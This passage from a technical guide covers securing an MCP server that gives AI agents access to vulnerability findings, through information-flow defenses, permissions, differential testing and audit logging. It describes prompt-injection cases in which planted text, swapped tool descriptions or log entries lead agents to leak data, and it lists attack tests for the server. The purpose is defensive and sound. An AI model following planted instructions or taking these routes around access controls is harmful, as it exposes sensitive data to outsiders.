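If the machine is unpatched, `b` stays true and still counts as public, so the interpreter allows the email. If the machine is patched, `b` becomes false and no email goes out, so the outsider learns the secret either way. CaMeL also reruns a program that fails, and whether a policy blocked it can depend on secret data, so repeated attempts can leak a secret bit by bit. Planted text can't make the planner write such a program, because the planner never reads it, but these leaks mean CaMeL lacks the kind of proof the findings server can have. Garby and colleagues built a small programming language for agents in which a computer-checked proof rules out leaks like the one through `b`.

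FIDES provably guarantees a weaker property than non-interference. The guarantee covers data that the agent passes along directly, but not what an observer can infer from which tools the agent calls. Costa and colleagues chose the weaker property because full non-interference would in effect forbid any call with publicly visible results after the agent had read something secret.

Protection can also fail when one agent passes data to another. Peters-Gill and colleagues had one CaMeL agent read a database of job applicants and another send a summary to a colleague. The coordinating agent pasted the summary into its instructions to the sending agent, which treated planted text in the summary as part of a trusted request and emailed the data to an outsider. Their fix sends instructions and data through separate channels and forbids anything derived from a tool's output in the instructions. On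 their benchmark, the attacks' average success rate was 12.9% without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL, and zero with the fix added.

Other successors try to block less legitimate work. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) adds two features to FIDES. The planner knows the policies in advance, and it can ask a person to vouch for a piece of data. If an email lists ten jobs, the person can approve the email once instead of approving ten calls. With OpenAI's o4-mini, approvals across the benchmark fell from 36.8 to 19.2 on average, while the completion rate fell from 75.7% to 73.2%. People may also read the requests more carefully when there are fewer of them.

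*CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) checks a CaMeL program before any tool runs. In one example, a security team's policy requires approval before anyone disconnects a machine from the network. If the program lacks that step, the checker returns a sequence of calls that breaks the rule, and the planner can use it to repair the program. When a policy would block a call, *APPA* (2026) searches for permitted ways to continue, such as obtaining a required approval.

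Labels cannot identify a bad instruction in a document that the user told the agent to obey. Only two of 1,296 attacks succeeded against Garby and colleagues' own agent. In both, the user had asked the agent to make whatever payment a file specified, and the attacker had replaced the file. An analyst who tells an agent to "do what the ticket says" creates the same problem.

CaMeL and FIDES also trust the user and the software that runs the agent. They protect against planted text, but an attacker who has stolen the analyst's credential can bypass them by running a script. The findings server's own limits still apply to that script.

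### Permissions for server processes

A malicious or compromised server can also steal data itself, without manipulating the agent. *AgentBound* (Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues, 2026) cites a server that appears to look up places on Google Maps but instead contacts a different network address, which it assembles from character codes. Such a server often runs with all the rights of the user who started it, so it could also read files and passwords on the analyst's computer.

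AgentBound adapts Android's permission model, in which each app declares the permissions it needs. A manifest lists the files, network destinations and secrets that a server may use, and a separate program runs the server and blocks access to everything else. The servers need no changes, and the checks added 0.6 milliseconds on average.

Bühler and colleagues collected the 296 most popular MCP servers and generated manifests automatically from servers' source code. Their reported accuracy of 80.9% is based on a smaller sample. They sent 96 manifests to the servers' developers, and those who replied judged 80.9% correct without changes. A company should still review each manifest, because an overly broad one can let data leave and an overly narrow one breaks the server.

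AgentBound wouldn't have stopped the theft at the start of this section, because the data left in an email and the email server needs permission to send email. But the invented company could use the same approach on its findings server by letting that server connect only to the data store, the directory, the ticket system and the sign-in service. A malicious update to one of the server's software libraries then couldn't send the table directly to an outsider.

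### Routes around the server

If a web log contains a working access token for the SIEM, an agent that can make web requests can use that token to search the SIEM directly, bypassing the findings server. Redaction removes some tokens before the agent sees them but misses others, so the company should also cancel any credential that turns up in a log and make its tokens expire quickly.

The computer the agent runs on is another source of credentials. Developers leave database passwords in configuration files, scripts and command histories, and an agent with a command line can search all of them within seconds. It may do this to finish a task, even when no attacker is involved. Claude Mythos 5.1 occasionally worked around broken permission checks for the same reason. The agent should run under its own account on a machine that holds no credentials for the data store.

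A stolen password is much less useful if the data store refuses connections from everywhere but the findings server. In PostgreSQL, an administrator can require this in the file that controls logins:

```text
# type    database   account      from           method
hostssl   findings   mcp_reader   10.0.5.12/32   scram-sha-256
```

If this is the only line that covers `mcp_reader`, PostgreSQL rejects connections to that account from any other address, even with the right password. A firewall in front of the database should also block those connections, in case someone later adds a broader line. The same limits have to cover backups, test copies and the SIEM's own web interface, because any of them may hold the same 60,000 rows.

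### What the model's provider receives

Unless the company runs the model itself, every answer that enters the model's context also goes to the model's provider. The host normally resends the whole conversation each time the model takes a turn, so in an investigation with 30 calls, it may send the first answer 30 times. This happens even without an attacker, and blocking the traffic with a firewall would disable the agent.

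The provider may keep the prompts for some time, for example to investigate misuse. The company should find out how long the provider keeps them, who can read them and whether it trains models on them, and write the answers into the contract. Returning fewer rows and columns also reduces the amount of data the provider can retain.

The company's own copies of the conversations need protection too. The host often saves them, and a gateway may log every answer in full. If these copies end up in the SIEM, a retail analyst's agent might find finance data in a finance analyst's saved conversation, much as Splunk's internal logs exposed users' tokens. The server could apply its rules correctly and still allow this, because nobody had marked the log entries as finance data. Conversation logs should carry the same restrictions as the most sensitive data in them.

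CaMeL can reduce what an outside provider learns. Its privileged model receives the analyst's request but not the results, so the company can use a strong hosted model for planning and run a smaller quarantined model on its own computers. FIDES as tested gives less privacy because it hides data from the planning model only when the data is untrusted. A scanner's findings would usually count as trusted, so the planning model's provider would receive the full list of unpatched machines. Costa and colleagues treated queries to the model as harmless, but they note that a company can also check its policies before those queries.

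A company that can't accept any disclosure has to run every model itself. It should then test how well its chosen model resists planted text, since at least one open-weight model did very badly in Gray Swan's measurements.

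## Testing and monitoring the boundary

These limits are code and configuration, and any of them may contain a mistake. A developer may have left the unit condition out of one tool, or an administrator may have given a test account access to the whole table. The company should attack its own server before an agent uses it, and again whenever something changes.

### Comparing two databases

The first tests replace the model with a program that sends `tools/call` messages containing whatever arguments the tester chooses. The guarantee has to hold for any agent, including this program.

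Leaving out the model also avoids two problems with evaluating agents. *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (April 2026), by the Australian Signals Directorate and five other cybersecurity agencies, warns that agents may behave differently during an evaluation and that small changes in wording can affect the results. A mediating server is ordinary code, so it gives a tester the same answers it would give an attacker.

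The tester needs two databases, A and B, that match on the permitted view and differ elsewhere. At the invented company, both contain the same 11,400 retail findings that agents may read. In B, the tester deletes, adds and changes findings among the other 48,600, which include the 600 on payment servers. If the analyst may also see counts for whole offices, those counts must match too. The tester can then swap the patch status of a patched and an unpatched machine in the same finance office, so that 7 of its 41 machines lack the patch in both databases.

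Each database gets its own copy of the server, and the program sends both copies the same calls:

```python
for trial in range(300):
    reset(server_a, server_b, seed=trial)
    history = []
    for step in range(30):
        call = next_call(history)     # random, may use earlier answers
        answer_a = send(server_a, token, call)
        answer_b = send(server_b, token, call)
        if answer_a != answer_b:
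            report(history, call, answer_a, answer_b)
            break
        history.append((call, answer_a))
```

Any difference disproves the guarantee, and the saved history lets a developer reproduce the difference. The program should compare entire responses, including row order, error text, status codes and headers. Sorting the rows first would hide the leak through tied findings described earlier. Timestamps and random handles would normally differ between the two copies, so the test build should use a fixed clock and the same random seed in both.

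Nearly all completely random arguments would fail the schema check and never reach the database. The test program should mostly send valid calls, change one thing at a time, and use names from the hidden rows. If it picked machine names at random from all 2,000, it would have only a 14% chance of naming fin-0009 at least once in 300 calls.

Timing tests need repeated measurements. With the 50-millisecond variation assumed earlier, 400 calls to each database leave an uncertainty of about 3.5 milliseconds in the difference between the averages, so the test can reliably detect only delays of about 7 milliseconds or more.

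The tester also has to check that the test fails when a limit is missing. One way is to remove the unit condition from a test build and turn off row-level security so that the database doesn't hide the mistake. The tester should then restore the condition and repeat the check for each of the other limits, one at a time. The tester should also use separate calls to confirm that permitted requests return the right rows, because a server that always returned nothing would pass the comparison.

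### Marked records and targeted attacks

Next, the tester plants records in the finance findings, the payment-server findings and the column of administrators' notes. Each record contains a unique string, such as `zq-fin-7c41e9`, that should never appear in an answer to the retail analyst. A program searches every answer, error message and header for these strings.

The comparison would already catch most of these leaks on the test databases, but a mark also shows which table the data came from. Marks work in places where the company can't run a comparison, such as the production system, outgoing email and saved conversations. Marks don't reveal leaks through counts, timing or reworded text.

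The tester then tries known kinds of attack:

| Test | What the program sends | Correct result |
|---|---|---|
| Nested query | A forbidden command inside a subsearch, a macro or a second statement | Refusal |
| Forged argument | `"business_unit": "finance"`, a quotation mark in `severity`, or the same field twice | Refusal |
| Mismatched names | One tool in the HTTP header and another in the body | Refusal |
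| Hidden tool | A tool that the analyst's `tools/list` reply leaves out | Refusal |
| Bad token | An expired token, one for the travel-booking server, or one with an edited username | Status 401 before any query runs |
| Another user's handle | A finance analyst's handle with analyst-214's token | The same answer as for a made-up handle |
| Withdrawn rights | A valid call just after the analyst moves to another unit | No retail rows |

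The nested-query test applies to servers that accept free-form queries. Splunk's allowlist missed commands in subsearches until version 0.2.4.

The handle test became more important in July, when the Model Context Protocol (2026) replaced sessions with handles. Servers built around session IDs need changes, according to the Agentic AI Foundation, which now hosts the protocol. Developers making those changes could easily forget to tie the new handles to users.

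The last test is whether the server rechecks permissions on every call instead of relying on an earlier approval. The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners warn that an attacker can exploit an outdated approval if the server doesn't recheck.

### Testing with a live model

Once the server passes, the company connects the real host, model and tools to the test system and puts hostile text in usernames, browser strings and tickets, including fake administrator notes and plausible cover stories. The tester should keep two results separate. The first is whether any marked record from outside the permitted view reaches the agent. None ever should, and even one means the server has a flaw or the agent has a route around it. The second is how often the model sends retail data elsewhere or gives the analyst a false report, a rate that will change with the model.

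An agent can respond differently to the same prompt, so one safe response to a planted username is weak evidence that the boundary holds. The agencies recommend varying the agent's tools and environment, and sampling several responses to the same prompt to see its full range of behavior.

Yang, Zheng and colleagues (2026) argue in *Securing the AI Agent* that each part of such a system needs its own kind of test. Their open-source tool matches known software against more than 1,400 vulnerability rules, uses a language model to audit the code of MCP servers, and probes live agents through multi-turn conversations. It plants marked strings to confirm leaks. It also treats the code it audits as untrusted, because that code may contain instructions to the auditing model. An audit like this may find mistakes that random calls miss, but a clean report from a language model doesn't establish that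 the boundary is secure.

### What a pass means

Suppose all 300 trials of the comparison pass. If a share *p* of such trials would reveal a difference, the chance of 300 clean ones is (1 − *p*)³⁰⁰. Setting this to 5% gives:

```text
p = 1 − 0.05^(1/300) ≈ 0.0099
```

If 300 independent trials of 30 calls each produce no failures, the tester can say with 95% confidence that the failure rate per trial is below about 1%. If the rate were 1% or more, 300 clean trials would occur less than 5% of the time. When there are no failures, the upper limit on the rate is roughly 3 divided by the number of trials, so lowering it to 0.1% takes about 3,000 clean trials. The 9,000 calls don't count as 9,000 trials because the calls within a trial build on one another and so aren't independent.

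A 1% failure rate would still be far too high, because a script making 10 calls a minute could run 480 such trials a day, causing nearly five leaks on average.

The larger problem is that the rate applies only to calls the tester's program generates. Suppose the server fails for one argument value in a million. If the program picks values at random, its 9,000 calls will miss the flaw about 99% of the time, but an attacker who finds the value in the server's source code needs only one call. For a similar reason, the defenses that Nasr and colleagues broke had done well against fixed attacks.

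Narrow tools allow a much stronger test. `list_exposed_machines` accepts four severities, 3,651 ages and 50 limits, which makes 730,200 valid combinations. At 100 calls a second, a program can send all of them to both databases in about four hours. A free-form tool accepts far too many queries to test this way. Even the complete test covers only two databases and one call at a time, so the company also needs to show from the code that the tool never receives hidden rows.

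### How Microsoft evaluates the Sentinel server

Microsoft runs automated checks on every deployment of the Sentinel server before rollout. The checks confirm that tools run and produce usable output, and that common investigations, such as an agent finding a table and then querying it, work from start to finish. Microsoft doesn't rely on separate manual grading.

The invented company would benefit from copying the practice of testing every deployment. But Microsoft's published account describes no test in which a hostile caller tries to get data outside its role. Microsoft may run such tests without publishing them. Customers need their own tests either way, because they choose the roles and scopes that determine who can see which data.

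A customer can't easily run two copies of Microsoft's hosted service. The customer can instead send a set of calls as a restricted analyst, change some rows outside that analyst's scope, and send the same calls again. Other data may change between the two runs, so the test works best in a test workspace.

### What to record for each call

Even a perfect boundary lets a manipulated agent misuse the analyst's own rights, and the company needs records to notice this. In May 2026 the US National Security Agency (NSA) published guidance on MCP. The NSA's *Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (2026) recommends logging every tool call with its exact arguments, the identities involved and, where feasible, a hash of the result. The invented company's server could write this:

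```json
{
  "time": "2026-12-05T10:14:07Z",
  "user": "analyst-214",
  "agent": "soc-assistant",
  "incident": 4471,
  "tool": "list_findings",
  "arguments": {"severity": "critical", "min_days_open": 30, "limit": 20},
  "decision": "allowed",
  "rows_returned": 14,
  "result_hash": "b81f02..."
}
```

The server should also record refused calls, with the real reason for each refusal, which it withheld from the agent. The hash of an answer lets an investigator check whether a leaked list matches it. Like the codes that replace addresses, the hash needs a secret key. To find out which machines an attacker learned about, the company has to store the IDs of the returned rows.

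Splunk's tools run as the user who called them, so a username alone doesn't show whether the analyst or the agent ran a search. Radidiya explains that searches through the MCP server carry a provenance label into `_audit`, the index where Splunk records searches, so a security team can find agents' searches alongside everyone else's. In *MCP Watch*, Keske offers an add-on that flags agents' searches that cover all indexes or very long periods. It identifies agents from a list of usernames, which suits service accounts but probably includes the analyst's own searches when an analyst and an agent share an account.

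Microsoft records when someone creates or runs an MCP tool in Sentinel. A company has to turn on auditing in Purview, Microsoft's compliance service, before it can look at those records.

### Patterns to look for

| Pattern | Possible cause |
|---|---|
| Repeated refusals for one user | A missing permission or a script that is probing |
| Calls to tools outside the user's list | A script, because an ordinary agent sees only the listed tools |
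| Calls that are missing from the host's own log | A stolen credential |
| Far more new rows than usual for one incident | Copying |
| Counts over groups that differ by one machine | An attempt to work out a hidden fact |
| A handle that belongs to someone else | A leaked handle |

In *MCP security risks*, Mooney suggests alerts for sudden increases in calls or errors, unusual arguments and new users of sensitive tools. Alerting on a single pattern produces many false alarms. If agents make 20,000 calls a day and a rule wrongly flags 0.5% of them, analysts have 100 false alarms a day to check. Mooney therefore recommends combining signals, such as a burst of calls from a user who has just had several failed sign-ins. Mooney also suggests looking for characters like `;` and `|` in arguments. This works for simple values but not for SPL or KQL, where `|` appears in most normal queries.

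Splunk's *MCP Telemetry Dashboard* shows rejected queries, denied calls by user, failed tokens and source addresses. Splunk expects the share of rejected queries to be near zero, so a rise deserves attention. But most panels lag by 5 to 20 minutes, and the dashboard has no alerts. A script that retrieves 1,000 rows per call could copy the retail unit's findings before a panel updates. The company needs its own scheduled searches for urgent patterns, and its own archive if it wants to look back more than 60 days.

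Operators also need a quick way to stop an agent, as the Australian Signals Directorate (2026) advises in its July guidance. The invented company's server could suspend agents' access to one incident when they exceed their row budget for it, while the analyst continues by hand. In Splunk, an administrator can remove a user's `mcp_tool_execute` capability instead of invalidating everyone's tokens.

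### Logs that the agent can read

Audit records can leak information across the boundary. Suppose a finance analyst looks up the machine fin-0009. If the retail analyst's agent can search the log of tool calls, it can learn that the machine exists and that someone is investigating it. The test that compares databases A and B should therefore include other users' activity. A finance test user should do different things in each database, and the retail analyst's answers must stay the same.

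In Splunk, agents can search the `_audit` and `_internal` indexes if the user's role allows it, and Splunk's MCP server once wrote users' tokens to `_internal`. Sentinel's audit records can end up in `CloudAppEvents`, which is searchable in Microsoft's ordinary threat-hunting tool. Since Sentinel's MCP tools can run hunting queries, some analysts' agents may be able to read records about other agents.

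An attacker can also write to these logs. If a manipulated agent puts an instruction in the `severity` argument, the server rejects the call but records the text, and an agent that later reviews the log will read it. The joint guidance recommends giving agents no write access to logs. A server that records arguments can't fully follow that advice, but it can prevent agents from changing or deleting entries. The company should send a copy of the logs to a store that no investigating agent can access. An agent that helps review them can work from counts and typed values.

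### The joint guidance and the NSA's criticism of MCP

The six agencies recommend using agents only for low-risk, non-sensitive tasks and never giving them broad access to sensitive data. Taken literally, this rules out an agent that reads a list of unpatched machines. The Australian agency's July advice on agents in cyber defense seems less restrictive, since the agency expects benefits from careful use with monitoring and strong controls. The joint guidance also recommends expanding agents' access in stages. The invented company could start with an agent that receives only counts and add access to individual incidents once its tests and records show that the limits work.

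The agencies' other recommendations mostly fit the design in earlier sections. They want each agent to have its own identity, credentials to expire when a job ends, and the system to authorize every request. They also say people should decide which actions need approval, and companies should keep a list of approved tools and versions.

The NSA finds that MCP leaves several of these controls to whoever builds the server:

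| What the NSA finds lacking | What the invented company does |
|---|---|
| Authorization is optional | Requires a valid token on every request |
| The protocol can't exchange role permissions | Looks up the analyst's unit in its directory |
| The protocol sets no rules for renewing, revoking or reusing tokens | Uses short-lived tokens and tests revocation |
| Developers decide what to log | Records every call and refusal |
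| A server can change its tools without new approval | Compares the tools with an approved copy |

The NSA's criticism that the protocol doesn't tie sessions to identities was about the November 2025 revision and is now out of date. However, a server that accepts a handle without checking whose it is has the same weakness.

The NSA also recommends signing messages and giving them an expiry time. This helps against someone who alters or replays messages in transit, but not against a manipulated agent, because the agent's host would sign its requests too. The recommendation to scan the network for unauthorized MCP servers is more useful here, because a developer's forgotten test server with a database password would let an agent bypass every limit.

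### New tools, wider allowlists and changed descriptions

A server that passes a security test may fail it after an update. Version 1.3 of Splunk's server added the `rest` command to `splunk_run_query` without renaming the tool, so a company that approved tools only by name would have missed the change. Splunk's *MCP Server REST command support* shows how one query can now map every user to their roles and capabilities, which previously took three tool calls and manual work. The command is read-only and the user's permissions still apply, but such a map would help an intruder choose which account to steal. To keep agents from building one, administrators have to restrict the users' roles or withhold the search tool.

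An upgrade can also add new tools. Splunk turns its own platform tools on by default, so administrators should compare the tool list before and after upgrading and turn off any tools they haven't reviewed.

Tool descriptions also need monitoring. The NSA cites a demonstration in which a malicious server showed a harmless description at installation and replaced it after the second use. The new description caused the agent to expose WhatsApp messages from another, trusted server. A gateway can prevent this by comparing each tool's name, description and schema with an approved copy, and blocking the tool if anything differs. Tool lists stopped varying by connection in July, so one approved copy for each role is enough.

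This comparison doesn't detect code changes that leave the description the same. A company that runs its own server can pin the version and rerun all tests before each upgrade. A company that uses a hosted server, such as Sentinel's, should rerun them on a schedule, perhaps weekly.

### Splunk's August 2026 security release

On 19 August, Splunk (2026) disclosed CVE-2026-76404, a flaw in its MCP server that it rated 9.1 out of 10 for severity. The server's credential-management code rebuilt program objects from stored data without checking their type. A user with the admin role could exploit this to run any command on the operating system. That user already had wide powers in Splunk, but running commands on the machine could also let them control the server's code and log files.

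The fix was in version 1.2.1, which Splunk had released 84 days earlier, on 27 May. The release notes listed a dashboard and rate limits but no security fix, so a company that installed only updates marked as security fixes would have stayed vulnerable for those 84 days. Installing every update immediately also carries a risk, because version 1.3.0 in July added the `rest` command. With automated tests, the company can upgrade within days and still find out what new abilities each role has gained.

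The same release fixed a confused deputy vulnerability in a different product, the Splunk AI Toolkit. When a user opened the history of agent runs, the software replaced the user's session key with a system token before it searched. Users without the admin or power role could therefore run searches with system-level privileges. A test that compared the results of two ordinary accounts would probably have caught this.

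### A checklist for judging a server

- Send a call without a token, and one with a token for another service. The server should refuse both.
- Find out whose rights each query runs under, and whether the database enforces them if the server makes a mistake.
- If agents can write their own queries, list everything that the database account can read.
- Change only hidden data and repeat the same calls. The answers, errors and row order should stay the same.
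- Add up how many rows one incident's agents can obtain in total, including through repeated calls.
- Mark every returned field that an outsider can write into.
- List the agent's other tools and every other route to the data store.
- Pick a call from last week and try to establish who made it, what it returned and whether an agent can read the record.
- Ask who approves new tools, wider allowlists and changed descriptions, and when the tests last ran.
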